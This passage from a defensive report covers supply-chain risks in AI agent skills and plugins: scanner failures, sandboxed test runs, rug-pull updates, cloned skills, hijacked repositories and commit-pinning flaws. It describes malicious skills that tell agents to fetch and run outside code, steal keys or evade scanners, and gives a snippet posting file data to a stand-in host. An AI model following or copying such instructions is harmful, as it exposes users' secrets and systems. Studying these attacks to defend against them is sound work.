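Credentials and local settings were the most common cause of false alarms, accounting for 36% of the findings Yang and colleagues examined. For example, one scanner blocked a phone-call skill for sending an access key to the company that issued it, which is a normal way to log in. The maintainers of a library of research skills, described in *Scientific Agent Skills* (2026), found the same pattern in their own scan, where eight of the 11 skills with a critical finding openly named a credential-like variable in their headers.

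Scanners can wrongly flag instructions that strengthen human oversight. In *When Skills Tell Agents Not to Ask* (2026), such instructions accounted for 23% to 29% of the flags from most configurations. When the researchers asked the same language model only whether an instruction loosened oversight, it scored nearly twice as high as the best scanner on a measure that combines missed cases and false alarms.

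Yang and colleagues also improved skill-vetter by adding guidance to its prompt based on the errors they had found. With GPT-5.4, the average number of false alarms on 150 harmless skills fell from 66 to 9, and the scanner missed fewer malicious skills. A firm that runs its own scanner may therefore gain more from improving the prompt than from paying for a larger model.

Some legitimate code looks like malware. Trail of Bits found that Anthropic's skills for Office files contain a script that loads extra compiled code into the program LibreOffice to work around a restriction in some sandboxes. Cisco's scanner rated this a low to medium concern, apparently because the model accepted the explanation in the skill. That explanation was honest, but an attacker could write an equally convincing false one.

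### Following data from instructions into code

Scanners produce many false alarms and misses because they check instructions and code separately. In the malicious presentation skill described earlier, the "backup" instruction sounds routine and uploading a file is normal for some scripts, so the harm is visible only when the two are read together.

Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *From Instructions to Exploits*, built a scanner called SCS that turns the instructions into code and analyses everything as one program. A language model first translates SKILL.md into a small fixed vocabulary of operations, such as reading a file, running a script or sending data. Suppose the invoice skill told the agent to send its table to a backup server. The translation would look roughly like this:

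```python
v1 = read_file("output/invoices.csv")
http_post("https://backup.example", v1)
```

Ordinary software then checks the translation for invented functions and undefined variables, and sends faulty lines back to the model. SCS combines the translation with the skill's Python, JavaScript and shell scripts in a single data-flow graph.

Each value in the graph has three labels, which record how far its source can be trusted, how sensitive it is and which operations produced it. Trust and sensitivity are numbers, with higher values meaning greater risk. When two values with labels (*t*₁, *s*₁, *C*₁) and (*t*₂, *s*₂, *C*₂) combine, the result gets

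(max(*t*₁, *t*₂), max(*s*₁, *s*₂), *C*₁ ∪ *C*₂).

A key still counts as sensitive after a script encodes it or mixes it with harmless text. Fixed rules then look for dangerous combinations, such as a sensitive value reaching a network function. The language model translates but makes few of the security decisions, so the results should depend less on which model a firm uses.

SCS caught 95.2% of the malicious skills, averaged over five models, in a test on 117 malicious and 117 harmless skills, and 80.2% of the skills it flagged were malicious. The translation was fully correct for 92.5% to 94.5% of 400 instruction steps. SCS works best when a file's path shows that its contents are sensitive, as with an SSH key. It might not classify `invoices.csv` as confidential, so it could miss the upload in the example.

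### Why scanners miss malicious skills

Scanners do not read everything the agent will execute. *Cloak and Detonate* (Ji, Xu and colleagues, 2026) surveyed nine scanners, and all of them skipped some folders, file types or other content, partly to save time and avoid false alarms. Code that a skill downloads later is also missing from the files. A person has to check whatever the scanner skips.

Trail of Bits warns that an author can also adjust a skill until a public scanner passes it. In its June 2026 test, the company got past ClawHub's detector, Cisco's scanner and all three scanners on the marketplace skills.sh. Three of its four malicious skills took less than an hour to create.

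In a larger study, Ji and colleagues took 1,613 malicious skills from an archive of ClawHub, all matching published threat reports, and disguised them without changing their harmful behaviour. They tested eight scanners, using a sample of 100 skills for two that rely on a language model. With one form of disguise, each scanner missed at least 90% of the skills it had previously caught. In a separate test on 622 real malicious skills, another form of disguise reduced the detection rate of the best static scanner, Cisco's, from 99% to 10%.

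These results apply to attackers who study the scanner and adapt to it. Many attackers have not done so. Cisco's scanner with a language model caught 98.2% of the real malicious skills in Guo and colleagues' collection. Scanning is an easy way to remove such crude attacks, but a clean result is weak evidence that a skill is safe if it comes from a determined attacker.

A scanner can find the harmful part of a skill and still fail to reject it. Yang and colleagues found that in 151 of skill-vetter's 177 misses, the agent noticed the attack but did not reject the skill, often because the skill's own files contained no harmful code. In other cases, the agent advised the user to remove a dangerous step before installing. Reviewers should therefore read a scanner's findings as well as its verdict.

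### How a test run works

A skill has to take the same actions to steal a key however it is disguised. Ji and colleagues built a test-run system, SkillDetonate, that watches for those actions. It could test, for example, a malicious version of the invoice skill that steals the employee's SSH key.

SkillDetonate first installs the skill in a container and has an ordinary coding agent use it. Monitoring software records the system calls of every process the agent starts, including any program that `extract.py` launches.

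When the script tries to open the SSH key, a special file system returns a marker, such as `#data1`, instead of the contents, so the real key is never at risk. The skill's own files open normally. Any file that is neither part of the skill nor on the list of sensitive files appears not to exist.

Some skills write new instructions while they run. SkillDetonate detects a new instruction file in the skill's folder and gives it to the agent to follow in the same session. A scanner cannot read this file before installation because the file does not exist yet.

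SkillDetonate then tracks the marked data. If the agent repeats `#data1` in a command, the marker links that command to the data. If a program reads a marked file, SkillDetonate treats everything that program writes afterwards as sensitive, so compressing or encrypting the key does not hide it.

The verdict depends on two rules: the skill must not send sensitive data to a server outside an approved list, and it must not change files outside approved folders or install and run programs from untrusted sources. The script would break the first rule when it tried to send the stolen key.

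Ji and colleagues tested SkillDetonate on a benchmark of 150 malicious skills, each in its original form and two disguised ones. It detected 97% on average, with 2% false positives. Without data tracking, false positives rose to 16% because the system could no longer distinguish using a sensitive file from leaking it. Without the step that follows new instructions, detection of one disguised form fell from 95% to 30%.

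It detected an average of 87% of the 622 real malicious skills across the same three forms. The team had left out 81 others, including some that depended on outside services, because it could not reproduce them in a Linux sandbox. The detection rate for all real malicious skills may therefore be lower. A run took about two and a half minutes, compared with 21 seconds for Cisco's scanner.

### Comparing runs with and without the skill

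An agent may read files or contact servers whether or not a skill tells it to. *SkillSentry* (Li, Ying and colleagues, 2026) presents a system of the same name that tests which actions a skill causes. The system first scans the skill's files for suspicious behaviour and designs a task to trigger it. It then runs the task with and without the skill, from the same starting point, in an ordinary environment and again in one with a decoy, such as a fake credential. It raises an alarm only if the skill causes a completed action that its advertised purpose does not require.

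One skill was described as deleting temporary files only after the user confirmed. A scanner accepted this description, but when SkillSentry put decoy files in the folder and withheld confirmation, the skill deleted them anyway.

On two benchmarks, SkillSentry caught about 95% to 96% of malicious skills and flagged 2% to 4% of harmless ones. Skill-vetter did about as well on one of these benchmarks, catching 98.7% of malicious skills and flagging 3.9% of harmless ones. In four tests with disguised malicious skills, however, skill-vetter caught at most 22%, while SkillSentry caught 76% to 100%.

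When the researchers removed the initial scan and gave the agent general tasks, detection fell to between 4% and 8% on the same two benchmarks, because those tasks rarely met the conditions that triggered the harm. Testers can therefore use a scanner's findings to decide what to try, even when its verdict is unreliable.

The firm in the invoice example can do a simpler test run itself. It can put the skill, a few invented invoices and a fake SSH key in a disposable container, then log every file and connection the skill tries to open. If `extract.py` tries to read the key, the log will show it.

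### How many alarms are real?

A detection rate of 97% with 2% false positives sounds as if nearly every alarm must be right. Whether that is true depends on how many of the scanned skills are malicious. If *p* is that share, *d* the detection rate and *f* the false-positive rate, the share of alarms that are correct is

*pd* / (*pd* + (1 − *p*)*f*).

Suppose a marketplace tests 10,000 skills with SkillDetonate's benchmark rates. The lowest and highest shares in the table are close to those that Liu and colleagues and Koi found in their surveys:

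| Share malicious | True alarms | False alarms | Alarms that are correct |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.16% | 16 | 200 | 7% |
| 1% | 97 | 198 | 33% |
| 12% | 1,164 | 176 | 87% |

If 1% of 10,000 skills are malicious, the system catches 97 of the 100 malicious ones. It also flags 2% of the 9,900 harmless skills, so about two thirds of its alarms are false. At the rates in the first table, Cisco's scanner would produce about 95 true alarms and 1,762 false ones.

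The 2% rate is uncertain because it comes from only three false alarms in 150 runs. That result is compatible with a true rate from about 0.4% to 6%. At 6%, the marketplace would have 594 false alarms to check.

Zhao and colleagues saw the effect when they ran SCS on 66,157 ClawHub skills. It flagged 2,473, and they confirmed 627 of those as malicious through test runs and manual review, about 1% of the collection. About a quarter of the flagged skills were confirmed malicious, compared with 80% in their benchmark, where half of all the skills were malicious. They did not review the skills that SCS had passed, so the number of malicious skills it missed is unknown.

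False alarms are a much bigger problem for a marketplace than for a firm. A firm that tests 40 harmless skills would expect about one false alarm at a rate of 2% and seven at Cisco's 17.8%, few enough to investigate by hand. A marketplace that automatically blocks every flagged skill would remove thousands of legitimate ones.

### What test runs miss

A test run shows only what the skill does during that run. Harmful code may wait for a certain date or act only on a particular company's computers. A skill may also fetch a harmless file during the test and a malicious one a month later. Longer tests with realistic decoys help with some of these cases, but no test can cover every condition an attacker might choose.

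When SkillDetonate missed a real malicious skill, it was usually because the agent read the harmful instruction but did not follow it. The firm's own agent might follow that instruction if it uses a different model. Other attacks failed because they needed a server that had gone offline or an account that the test environment lacked. Some malicious skills could also detect a test environment and do nothing harmful in it.

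Testing skills one at a time cannot reveal harm that arises only when several run together. *Scan Before You Install* and *Benign in Isolation, Harmful in Composition* (2026) both demonstrate this risk with skills that are harmless or low-risk on their own.

When SkillSentry cannot trigger a suspicious behaviour, it returns "unresolved" instead of counting the skill as safe. A firm can likewise note in the approval record which functions the test run did and did not exercise. For `deploy.py`, a test with a fake credential and a dummy server would show where the script sends the pages, but someone would still need to read the code for conditions the test never met.

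## How can approved code change without a new approval?

A review covers the files as they were when somebody read them, but an approved skill may run hundreds of times afterwards. On each run, the agent uses whatever the skill's folder, its packages and any linked web pages contain at that moment. Programmers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use problem, because what was checked can change before it is used. The gap can last for months for an add-on, whereas inside one program it is often a fraction of a second, as with the network address that Sandlock copies before checking.

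Most changes made after approval are ordinary bug fixes and new features. Security researchers often call a hostile one a rug pull. Hostile changes arrive by the same routes as ordinary ones, so a firm can't catch them by watching only for suspicious events.

### Automatic updates

By default, Claude Code automatically updates plugins from most of Anthropic's official marketplaces and from marketplaces that a user adds from a claude.ai account. Automatic updates are off by default for all other marketplaces, including third-party marketplaces and the community marketplace. Anthropic automatically screens plugins in the community marketplace and ties each catalogue entry to one commit, a saved state of the plugin's repository.

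When automatic updates are on, Claude Code checks the marketplace after a session starts and replaces the plugin's files on disk. The current session keeps the old version, and a message names the updated plugin but doesn't describe what changed. The next session loads the new version without prompting the user.

To turn off automatic updates, the user types `/plugin`, opens the Marketplaces tab, selects the marketplace and chooses "Disable auto-update". The "Update marketplace" option in the same tab is easy to misread, because it refreshes the catalogue and also updates nearly all the plugins the user installed from that marketplace. A firm that wants to see what is new before installing it can instead run `claude plugin marketplace update` in a terminal, which refreshes only the catalogue.

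Plugins that a user or an organization has turned on in a claude.ai account sync each time the user starts Claude Code in a terminal while signed in to that account. A separate setting turns this sync off, so a firm that disables automatic updates for every marketplace should check that setting as well.

Visual Studio Code also installs new versions of extensions automatically by default. The user can turn this off for a single extension, or for all of them with the `extensions.autoUpdate` setting. A skill folder that someone copied by hand, like the one in the invoice example, stays as it is until someone replaces it.

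### Harmful releases under a trusted name

When automatic updates are on, an attacker can get a harmless release installed and then deliver malicious code as an update. The Hacker News describes an extension for Solidity, a programming language for the Ethereum blockchain. On 31 October 2025, its publisher released a harmless version, 0.0.7, on Open VSX, a registry that serves the code editor Cursor. Version 0.0.8, released on 1 November, contained SleepyDuck, a trojan that let the attacker control the computer remotely. The trojan started when the user opened an editor window or a Solidity file, and it checked for new commands every 30 seconds.

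The attacker seems to have planned the change from the start. SleepyDuck looks up the address of its control server in a record on the blockchain, and the attacker created that record on the day the harmless version, 0.0.7, came out. The Eclipse Foundation's *Open VSX security update, October 2025* (2025) had just announced that the registry would scan extensions at publication. It is unclear whether the scans were running yet, but a scan of version 0.0.7 would have found nothing wrong.

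Secure Annex, which sells extension security, reported that the extension had 14,000 recorded downloads before it turned harmful. Its researcher John Tuckner thought the attacker had probably inflated the count to rank higher in search results. The number of victims is unknown.

Some publishers release many working versions before adding harmful code. postmark-mcp was an MCP server for sending email through Postmark. Koi found that its first 15 versions worked properly, but version 1.0.16 added a line that secretly copied the developer on every email the agent sent. Those emails could include invoices and password resets.

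Postmark had nothing to do with the package. The developer had copied the company's public code and published it under the same name on npm, the main registry for JavaScript packages. A reviewer who read only the code would have rightly approved any of the 15 clean versions, but checking with Postmark before the first installation would have revealed the impersonation.

A sandbox would probably not have helped either. Postmark itself delivered the hidden copies along with the originals, so a network rule that allowed only Postmark's address would have let them through. Comparing version 1.0.16 with the previous version would have revealed the change immediately.

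Koi estimated that the package exposed about 300 organizations, assuming that a fifth of its 1,500 weekly downloads were in active use. ThaiCERT's *Researchers Discover First Malicious MCP Server in Rogue Postmark-MCP Package* reports just over 1,643 downloads in total before the package disappeared from npm, barely more than one week at Koi's rate. Koi, which sells protection against such packages, called its own figures guesses, and they may be much too high. There is better reason to trust its warning that copies already on users' machines kept working and forwarding email after the developer deleted the package from npm.

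### The cloned skills on skills.sh

The largest of these campaigns by recorded installations involved the marketplace skills.sh, which the company Vercel runs. Zenity Labs' *Attackers Target Agents via The Skill Supply Chain* traces how an attacker copied the whole repository of Paperclip, a popular AI tool, including the skills its authors supply, and published it under a similar name. Holding back the harmful part let the copies collect installations first:

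| Date in 2026 | What the attacker changed | What a review of the skill files would have found |
|---|---|---|
| 5 July | Nothing yet; skills.sh first recorded installations | Exact copies of the real skills |
| 6 July | Added malicious code to the Paperclip program in the same repository | Still nothing wrong |
| 11 July | Added a setup guide that told agents to download and run outside code | The harmful instruction, in a secondary file |
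| 30 July | Made the program's installation start the same kind of download automatically | The setup guide, but not the new trigger |

The main file of each skill described a legitimate task. An agent opened the setup guide only when Paperclip was missing, so it might never have opened the guide for a user who already had the program. The guide described the attacker's copy as the only supported way to install Paperclip and warned agents not to use the real package. The downloaded code searched more than 100 locations for SSH keys, cloud credentials and other secrets.

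Nobody had to approve the skill's listing on skills.sh. According to *Context Matters* (Holzbauer, Schmidt and colleagues, 2026), the marketplace adds a skill when someone installs it with the marketplace's command-line tool, provided the tool is set to report usage. The marketplace runs scanners, but on 5 July they would have scanned clean files.

The same attacker also published two malicious packages on PyPI, the main registry for Python packages. Other researchers identified one in under two hours and the other within an hour. The skills stayed on skills.sh for three weeks after they became harmful, and they were on its trending list for much of July. Outside teams routinely examine new releases on PyPI, and this comparison suggests that skill marketplaces need the same continuous monitoring. Checking each skill only when it first appeared would have missed this campaign.

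The 1.7 million installations mentioned earlier are the total for this family of skills up to 2 August. Zenity, which sells security for AI agents, stresses that this is not a count of victims, and one user may have installed several skills. Orca Security also found that one skill marketplace accepted installation reports without checking who sent them.

The total also includes installations from before 11 July. Those copies would stay clean until someone updated them, so the early installations mainly gave the listing a good reputation, which attracted the later victims.

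Vercel and GitHub removed the skills and repositories within 12 hours of Zenity's report. Users who had already installed a harmful copy still had to remove it by hand, as The Next Web points out in *Malicious AI ‘skills’ turned agents into credential thieves, at scale*.

### Version labels and dependencies

A version label can also point to new files. In Git, the version-control system that GitHub is built on, a branch name such as `main` refers to the newest commit on that branch, so it moves with every change. A tag such as `v1.3` normally stays in place, but the repository's owner can delete it and give the same name to a different commit. If the approval record for the invoice skill contained only "version 1.3", an employee who reinstalled the skill from that tag could get files that nobody had reviewed. Package registries tend to be stricter. On npm, for example, a publisher cannot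 use the same version number twice.

Git calculates a commit's identifier from its contents, so recording the identifier prevents this kind of change as long as the runtime checks the downloaded code against it. AIR's *Plugin4Shell* (2026) reports that Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI all failed to do this check properly, a flaw covered in the next section.

Dependencies can change while every file in the skill stays the same. In the earlier example, `uv run` can download the newest pdfplumber when `extract.py` starts. An `npx` command that starts an MCP server has a similar weakness if it names a package without a version. The user approves the command once, but the package's publisher can later change the code it fetches.

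Sometimes the code doesn't exist yet when the review happens. In *Agent Skills Are Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands*, Eriksen of the security company Aikido describes an npm package called `react-codeshift` that a language model had made up. People copied, adapted and translated the skill files that mentioned it, until 237 GitHub repositories contained instructions for agents to install a package that nobody had published. Eriksen registered the name in January 2026 with an empty package and soon saw downloads, some from agents following the instructions.

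A reviewer could have read every line of such a skill without finding anything malicious, and would have noticed the problem only by looking up the package. Attackers also claim package names in advance. Zenity (2026) found hundreds of names that someone had reserved with empty packages for later use.

### Content fetched at run time

In June 2026, the security company AIR tested how far a skill could get if its harmful part was on a web page. The skill, `brand-landingpage`, offered to build a web page with Google's design tool Stitch. AIR advertised it on Instagram to marketers and designers. The skill contained no malicious code, but it told the agent to rely on an online documentation page, install whatever software the page called for and not bother the user with the details.

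In *Anatomy of a Malicious AI Skill*, Hoppe (2026) reconstructed the test from the traces it left on GitHub. He points out that a careful author could write the same instructions for a new and fast-changing tool. Only the address was wrong, because it contained the name Stitch but belonged to AIR.

According to The Hacker News (2026), AIR submitted the skill to a GitHub collection with about 36,000 stars, which accepted it after a few days. Scanners from Cisco and NVIDIA, and those that skills.sh uses, also rated it safe. During these checks, the link led to Google's real documentation. Once enough people had installed the skill, AIR replaced the page with instructions to download and run a script. The script only sent the user's email address to AIR.

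AIR says it reached about 26,000 agents, some of them on company accounts. Nobody else has confirmed this, and AIR published the figure while preparing to launch its own marketplace. The weakness is real whatever the true number, because the scanners examined only the files in the package. Trail of Bits had got past several of the same scanners three weeks earlier.

Pinning the skill to a commit would not have helped its users, because none of its files changed. They could have noticed the attack only by recognizing that the address was not Google's, and the skill's instructions hid the installation from them. In September 2026, Hoppe found that the file was still in the collection. If AIR gives up the domain, the next owner could send new instructions to every agent that still has the skill.

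Snyk classed external addresses that control an agent's behaviour as a medium risk in its scan of ClawHub. That seems too low for a skill that also tells the agent to install what it finds there. The agent follows those instructions with the user's permissions, which is much more dangerous than a person reading a documentation link.

### Remote servers

The operator of a remote MCP server can replace its code at any time without changing a file on the user's machine or announcing a new version. Suppose the firm sends its invoices to a remote service that checks suppliers' tax numbers. If the operator began to keep a copy of every invoice, the service's answers would look the same. A new owner, a thief with the operator's password or a careless employee could cause the same leak.

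A runtime can compare the server's tool definitions with the ones the firm approved, and a later section covers which differences should matter. But the firm can't tell from these definitions what happens to data after sending it. It has more control over what it sends. For example, it could give the tax service only the supplier's name and number, without the prices or bank details.

### Projects that change hands

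Someone the reviewer never considered can take over a repository and change the approved code. The company AIR reports in its SkillJacking study that 925 skills already in use "were hijacked out from under their maintainers" through their repositories, affecting 134,000 agents. Both figures come from AIR alone. Any review these skills had passed would have covered the original owner's files, but the new owner could publish different files at the same address.

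Holzbauer and colleagues studied how someone could replace approved code by taking over its repository's address. Many marketplaces store only a link to a GitHub repository. When a project's owner changes their account name, GitHub redirects the old address to the new one, but other people can then claim the old name. Anyone who does may be able to put a new repository at the address the marketplace still lists. GitHub retires the names of heavily downloaded repositories to prevent this, but less popular ones remain exposed.

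Holzbauer and colleagues found seven abandoned repositories that an attacker could have claimed, with 121 skills depending on them. They registered the old account names and kept them so that nobody else could. The skills were not very popular. Those on skills.sh had a median of 25 downloads and a maximum of 2,032. AIR's total of 134,000 agents looks surprisingly large beside these figures, but the two results aren't directly comparable because Holzbauer and colleagues tested only repositories with at least five stars and only this one method of takeover.

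A marketplace can largely prevent such takeovers by storing the files itself, as ClawHub does. The firm in the invoice example gets the same protection by keeping its own copy of the skill.

Stolen credentials give an attacker control of a project without any visible change of owner. On 26 November 2026, AIR reported a campaign it calls TrojanPony. According to *AI Skills 暗藏木馬！駭客竊取憑證、487個GitHub儲存庫遭波及* (2026), an article in Taiwan's *Liberty Times*, attackers hid trojans in imitations of popular programming skills and stole the access credentials of developers who installed them. They then used those credentials to infect other software projects. The article reports that 487 GitHub repositories were affected.

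An add-on can also replace another one. Zenity found a skill that uninstalled Claude's own tool for creating skills and took its place without telling the user. A sandbox that blocks writes to the skills folder, as Claude Code's does, should stop a script from doing this.

### Who controls each route

| Route | Who can make the change | Case | Could the user have noticed? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Automatic update | The publisher, unless the user has turned updates off | SleepyDuck | Only from a new version number, unless someone compared the two releases |
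| New release that the user installs | The publisher | postmark-mcp; the cloned Paperclip skills | Yes, by comparing the new files with the old; the hidden recipient could also appear in email logs |
| Moved version label | The repository's owner | None described here | Yes, if the approval record includes the commit or a digest |
| Dependency chosen at each run | The package's publisher, or whoever registers an unused name | `react-codeshift` | Only by checking which packages the agent had installed |
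| Content fetched at run time | Whoever controls the web address | AIR's test skill | Hardly; the files stayed the same, and the only clue was an unfamiliar address |
| Remote server | Its operator | None described here | No, unless the answers or tool definitions also changed |
| Project that changes hands | The new owner, or a thief with the owner's credentials | SkillJacking; TrojanPony | Sometimes, from a new maintainer or unexpected commits, but the address stays the same |
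| Replacement by another add-on | The other add-on's author | The imitation of Claude's skill-creation tool | Yes, by comparing the installed folder with the approved copy |

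## How do pins, hashes and signatures tie a script to the version that was reviewed?

To keep running the version it reviewed, a firm needs a record that identifies that version. The record can be as weak as a version number, which is only a name, or as strong as a digest calculated from every file the script uses. Even with a strong record, the runtime has to compare it with the files before they run. Four widely used coding agents skipped this comparison for plugins pinned to a commit, and two of them still had no fix in late September 2026.

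### Labels, digests and commits

In Git, a repository's owner can move a version label such as "1.3" to different files. *Skills Are Not Islands* (Jia, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) analysed 1.43 million skills listed on skillsmp.com and found a version in only 20% of them. About 59% of all the skills shared their name with at least one other skill, usually one with different contents. A name and version such as "invoice-extraction 1.3" could therefore refer to several unrelated folders.

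A SHA-256 digest is a 64-character string calculated only from a file's bytes, whatever the file's length. Changing one letter of the file changes the digest, and nobody knows a practical way to make a second file with the same digest. The firm calculates the digest when it approves the skill and again before running it. If the two digests differ, the file has changed, and somebody still has to look at the change to find out whether the author corrected a typing error or added a backdoor.

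The firm has to store the digest somewhere that people who can change the skill cannot edit. A digest published beside the download offers little protection against a stolen password, because the thief can replace both.

A commit identifier is also a digest, which Git calculates from a snapshot of the whole repository and its history. One identifier covers SKILL.md, `extract.py` and every other file in the repository, but not pdfplumber or a web page that the skill opens. Most repositories still use the older SHA-1 algorithm, and in 2017 researchers produced two different files with the same SHA-1 digest. Git rejects files made with the known technique, but SHA-256 is the better choice for the firm's own record.

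### Lockfiles

A lockfile extends the pin to packages. Two lines from the invoice skill's lockfile might look like this, with invented versions and shortened digests:

```
pdfplumber==0.12.1 --hash=sha256:5d1e...
pillow==12.4.0 --hash=sha256:71ac...
```

The skill doesn't mention the imaging library Pillow, but pdfplumber needs it. With `--require-hashes`, pip refuses to install any package that is missing from the list or whose downloaded file has a different digest. A lockfile with only version numbers is weaker because it relies on the registry to keep supplying the same files.

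Few skill authors give reviewers a list of dependencies to start from. Jia and colleagues found a field for dependencies in 1.4% of skills, although 37% depended directly on a package, another skill or an outside service. Their figures come from an automated tool that made few errors on 500 skills labelled by hand.

Skills that reuse other skills are the hardest to lock. One skill for designing web pages in the style of Windows 95 named three other skills and no packages, but those three brought in 1,754 packages. Across the collection, more than 70% of the links between skills and packages from npm or PyPI came through a reused skill, so a reviewer who locked only the packages a skill names itself would miss most of them. Jia and colleagues recommend that developers keep a record, like a lockfile, of the pinned version and source repository of everything a skill reuses.

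A lockfile controls installation only. Once the packages are on the disk, pip doesn't check them again when `extract.py` runs.

### Signatures and build records

A publisher signs a release by combining the release's digest with a private key that nobody else should have. Anyone with the matching public key can check that the holder of the private key signed exactly those files.

A signature shows who released the code but does not show that the code is safe. The developer of postmark-mcp could have signed the version that secretly copied every email, and the signature would have been valid. Checking the signature could still have helped before the first installation, because a firm that expected Postmark's own key would have noticed that somebody else had published the package. A firm therefore has to decide in advance whose signatures it will accept.

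An old release keeps its valid signature even after a newer release fixes a vulnerability in it. *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts* (2026) proposes a signed manifest with a version number that can only increase, so that a runtime rejects an older release once it has encountered a newer one. The manifest also lists the capabilities the skill may use. Because the signature covers both the manifest and the skill's content, nobody can add capabilities to the list without invalidating the signature.

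Several existing systems make signing safer or add information about where a package came from:

- *Sigstore* lets a developer sign with an existing account instead of a permanent key. It issues a certificate that is valid for minutes and enters it in a public log. There is no long-lived key to steal, but a thief who gets into the account can sign too. The developer can discover this from the log, if anyone is watching it.
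- *The Update Framework* protects a registry's update system when an attacker steals some of its keys. It divides the work among several keys and can require more than one signature for important changes. Its signed records also expire, which keeps an attacker from offering an outdated release indefinitely. It doesn't protect users from a harmful release by an authorized publisher.
- *SLSA* (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts) sets requirements for records of how someone built a package, including the source and the build system. A trustworthy record can expose a package that its publisher did not build from the public repository. If the source itself contains a backdoor, the record will accurately describe how the backdoor got into the package.

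Zhu and Wang (2026) point out in *Versioned Transitive Dependency-Closure Binding and Operation-Time Effect Governance for Agent Skills* that, under SLSA, whoever produces a build record decides how complete it is, and checking the dependencies' own records is an additional step. Build records are most useful for packages and MCP servers. Many skills have no build step because users copy the author's folder. A digest is enough to compare that copy with the original.

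### Plugin4Shell: the missing check

A marketplace can pin each plugin to a reviewed commit, and an agent installing the plugin should get only that commit. On 17 September 2026, AIR disclosed a flaw in how agents handle these pins, which it calls Plugin4Shell. Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI all requested the pinned commit, but none checked that they had received it. Git can interpret the same name in more than one way, so whoever controlled a plugin's repository could make the request return other code, and the agent would still treat the installation as correctly pinned.

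The missing check is short. According to The Next Web, the agent needs one more line of code, which looks up the commit that is actually in the working folder and stops unless it matches the pin. A reviewer can do the same by hand in any folder that Git manages:

```
git rev-parse HEAD
```

This command prints the identifier of the current commit, which the reviewer compares with the one in the approval record. It doesn't reveal uncommitted edits, so the reviewer should also run `git status`.

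Even careful firms were exposed, since AIR stresses that the victim only had to have a reviewed and pinned plugin from a trusted marketplace. The attacker could be the plugin's author or someone who had taken over its repository, as in SkillJacking. Automatic updates used the same faulty step, so if they were on when a marketplace moved a pin to a newer reviewed commit, the wrong code could reach an installed plugin without any action by the user.

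Help Net Security's *Zero-click RCE vulnerability hit four major AI coding agents, two remain unpatched* reports working demonstrations against all four agents, but no attacks on users. AIR found the flaw in May and told the vendors in June. AIR sells a marketplace and a filter that it says were not affected, so it has an interest in making the flaw sound serious. Still, the evidence for the flaw is much stronger than the evidence for AIR's counts of reachable agents, because Anthropic and OpenAI both changed their products in response.

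| Agent | Fixed version | Status in late September 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 2.1.179, released on 16 June | Anthropic confirmed the fix to AIR, but the release notes do not mention it |
| Codex | 0.146.0 | The changelog lists the new check, and AIR verified it on 12 August |
| GitHub Copilot | None | GitHub and AIR disagree about the exposure |
| Gemini CLI | None planned | Google is retiring it and advises users to move to Antigravity |

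IlSoftware.it's *Plugin4Shell, falla zero-click negli agenti AI* reports that GitHub responded by saying its platform blocks branch and tag names that imitate commit identifiers. The researchers replied that Copilot can also install plugins from other hosts, some of which allow such names. A firm that installs Copilot plugins only from GitHub avoids this form of the flaw, and AIR accepts that this restriction helps. But Copilot's documentation describes a pinned plugin as safe from later changes to its branches, and that should be true wherever the code is hosted.

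Gemini CLI had a different form of the flaw, which restricting the hosts doesn't prevent. Google told AIR on 4 August that it would not fix the flaw. Help Net Security reports that Antigravity has no comparable system for pinning plugins. Users who move to Antigravity avoid the faulty check, but they need another way to keep a reviewed version, such as a private copy.

The technology site Digital Matters checked the vendors' pages on 27 September and found no Copilot fix and no entry for the flaw in CVE, the public list of known vulnerabilities. A firm that relies on CVE alerts or release notes could easily have missed the Claude Code fix. Such a firm should compare its installed versions with the table and check Copilot's changelog for a later correction.

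### Checking the files at load time

A runtime could also verify each skill at load time. *Sealing the Audit-Runtime Gap for LLM Skills* (Shen, Feng and colleagues, 2026) presents SIGIL, which combines a registry of approved skills with a loader inside the agent's software. The registry makes any change to an approved record detectable. Before a skill's text enters the model's context, the loader compares the skill with its approved record and applies the permissions approved for it.

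In tests, SIGIL stopped all the attacks that altered a skill on the user's machine after approval. Speed is a poor reason to skip the check, since the comparison took less than half a millisecond and contacting the registry took an average of 52 to 158 ms, depending on the registry's database.

In SIGIL, a committee approves skills. Its members stake tokens on their votes, and the design assumes that honest members will keep most of the voting weight. A firm that reviews its own skills doesn't need the committee. It could use SIGIL's simplest publication type, which puts only a digest in the registry and leaves the skill on the owner's device. But the loader must be the only way to load a skill, and the firm can't ensure that on its own if its runtime offers other ways.

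### Which files does an approval have to cover?

A matching digest of SKILL.md doesn't show whether someone has changed `extract.py`. In *When the Approved File Is Unchanged* (October 2026), Hossen measured how often this kind of change happens in ordinary software projects, using 20 public repositories in which an approved file depends on other files. The approved file was typically a deployment workflow, a list of commands that an automation service runs. Those commands read other files that determine what the service deploys and with which permissions.

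Hossen went through 5,251 commits and found 542 that changed a file the run reads. In 296 of them (54.6%), the approved file stayed the same, so a digest of that file alone would not have revealed the change. These were normal edits by developers, not attacks.

One repository accounted for 130 of the 296 commits, and without it the share falls to 43.6%. Hossen also chose the repositories because their approved files depend on others, so the figure is not an estimate for skills. Many skills do have the same structure, though, with a short SKILL.md that sends the agent to scripts.

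Hossen edited copies of two of the projects to show what such a change can do. In one, the edit left an approved workflow unchanged but altered a file it used, giving a cloud role permission to write to a storage bucket. In the other, changing one line of a settings file reduced the human approvals required for high-risk changes from one to none. A check of the approved file accepted both edits.

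Hossen calls the files that a run's configuration tells it to read its *authority set*. Call this set *A*, and let *S* be the files whose contents an approval fixes. The approval is *sound* if *S* includes all of *A*, so that no file the run reads can change unnoticed. It is *exact* if *S* = *A*, which means that changes to unrelated files don't cancel it. Authority-set integrity is Hossen's name for soundness in this sense. An approval can fix files in four ways:

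- A *single-object binding* stores the path and digest of one file. It is sound only if the run reads nothing else.
- An *authority-set binding* stores one digest calculated over a chosen set of files. It is sound if the set includes everything the run reads, and exact if it includes nothing more.
- A *manifest binding* stores the digest of a list, which in turn contains the digests of other files. A lockfile has this form. The binding is only as complete as the list.
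- A *commit binding* stores a commit identifier, and the run uses that commit. It is sound for any file in the repository, but it is rarely exact, because the next commit ends the approval even if it only corrects the documentation.

An authority-set binding would have required a new approval for about one commit in ten in Hossen's sample. A single-object binding would have required fewer than half as many, but only because it would have missed the 296 changes. Hossen recommends a commit binding when a run can use a fixed commit. An authority-set binding is for approvals that must stay valid while the rest of the project changes.

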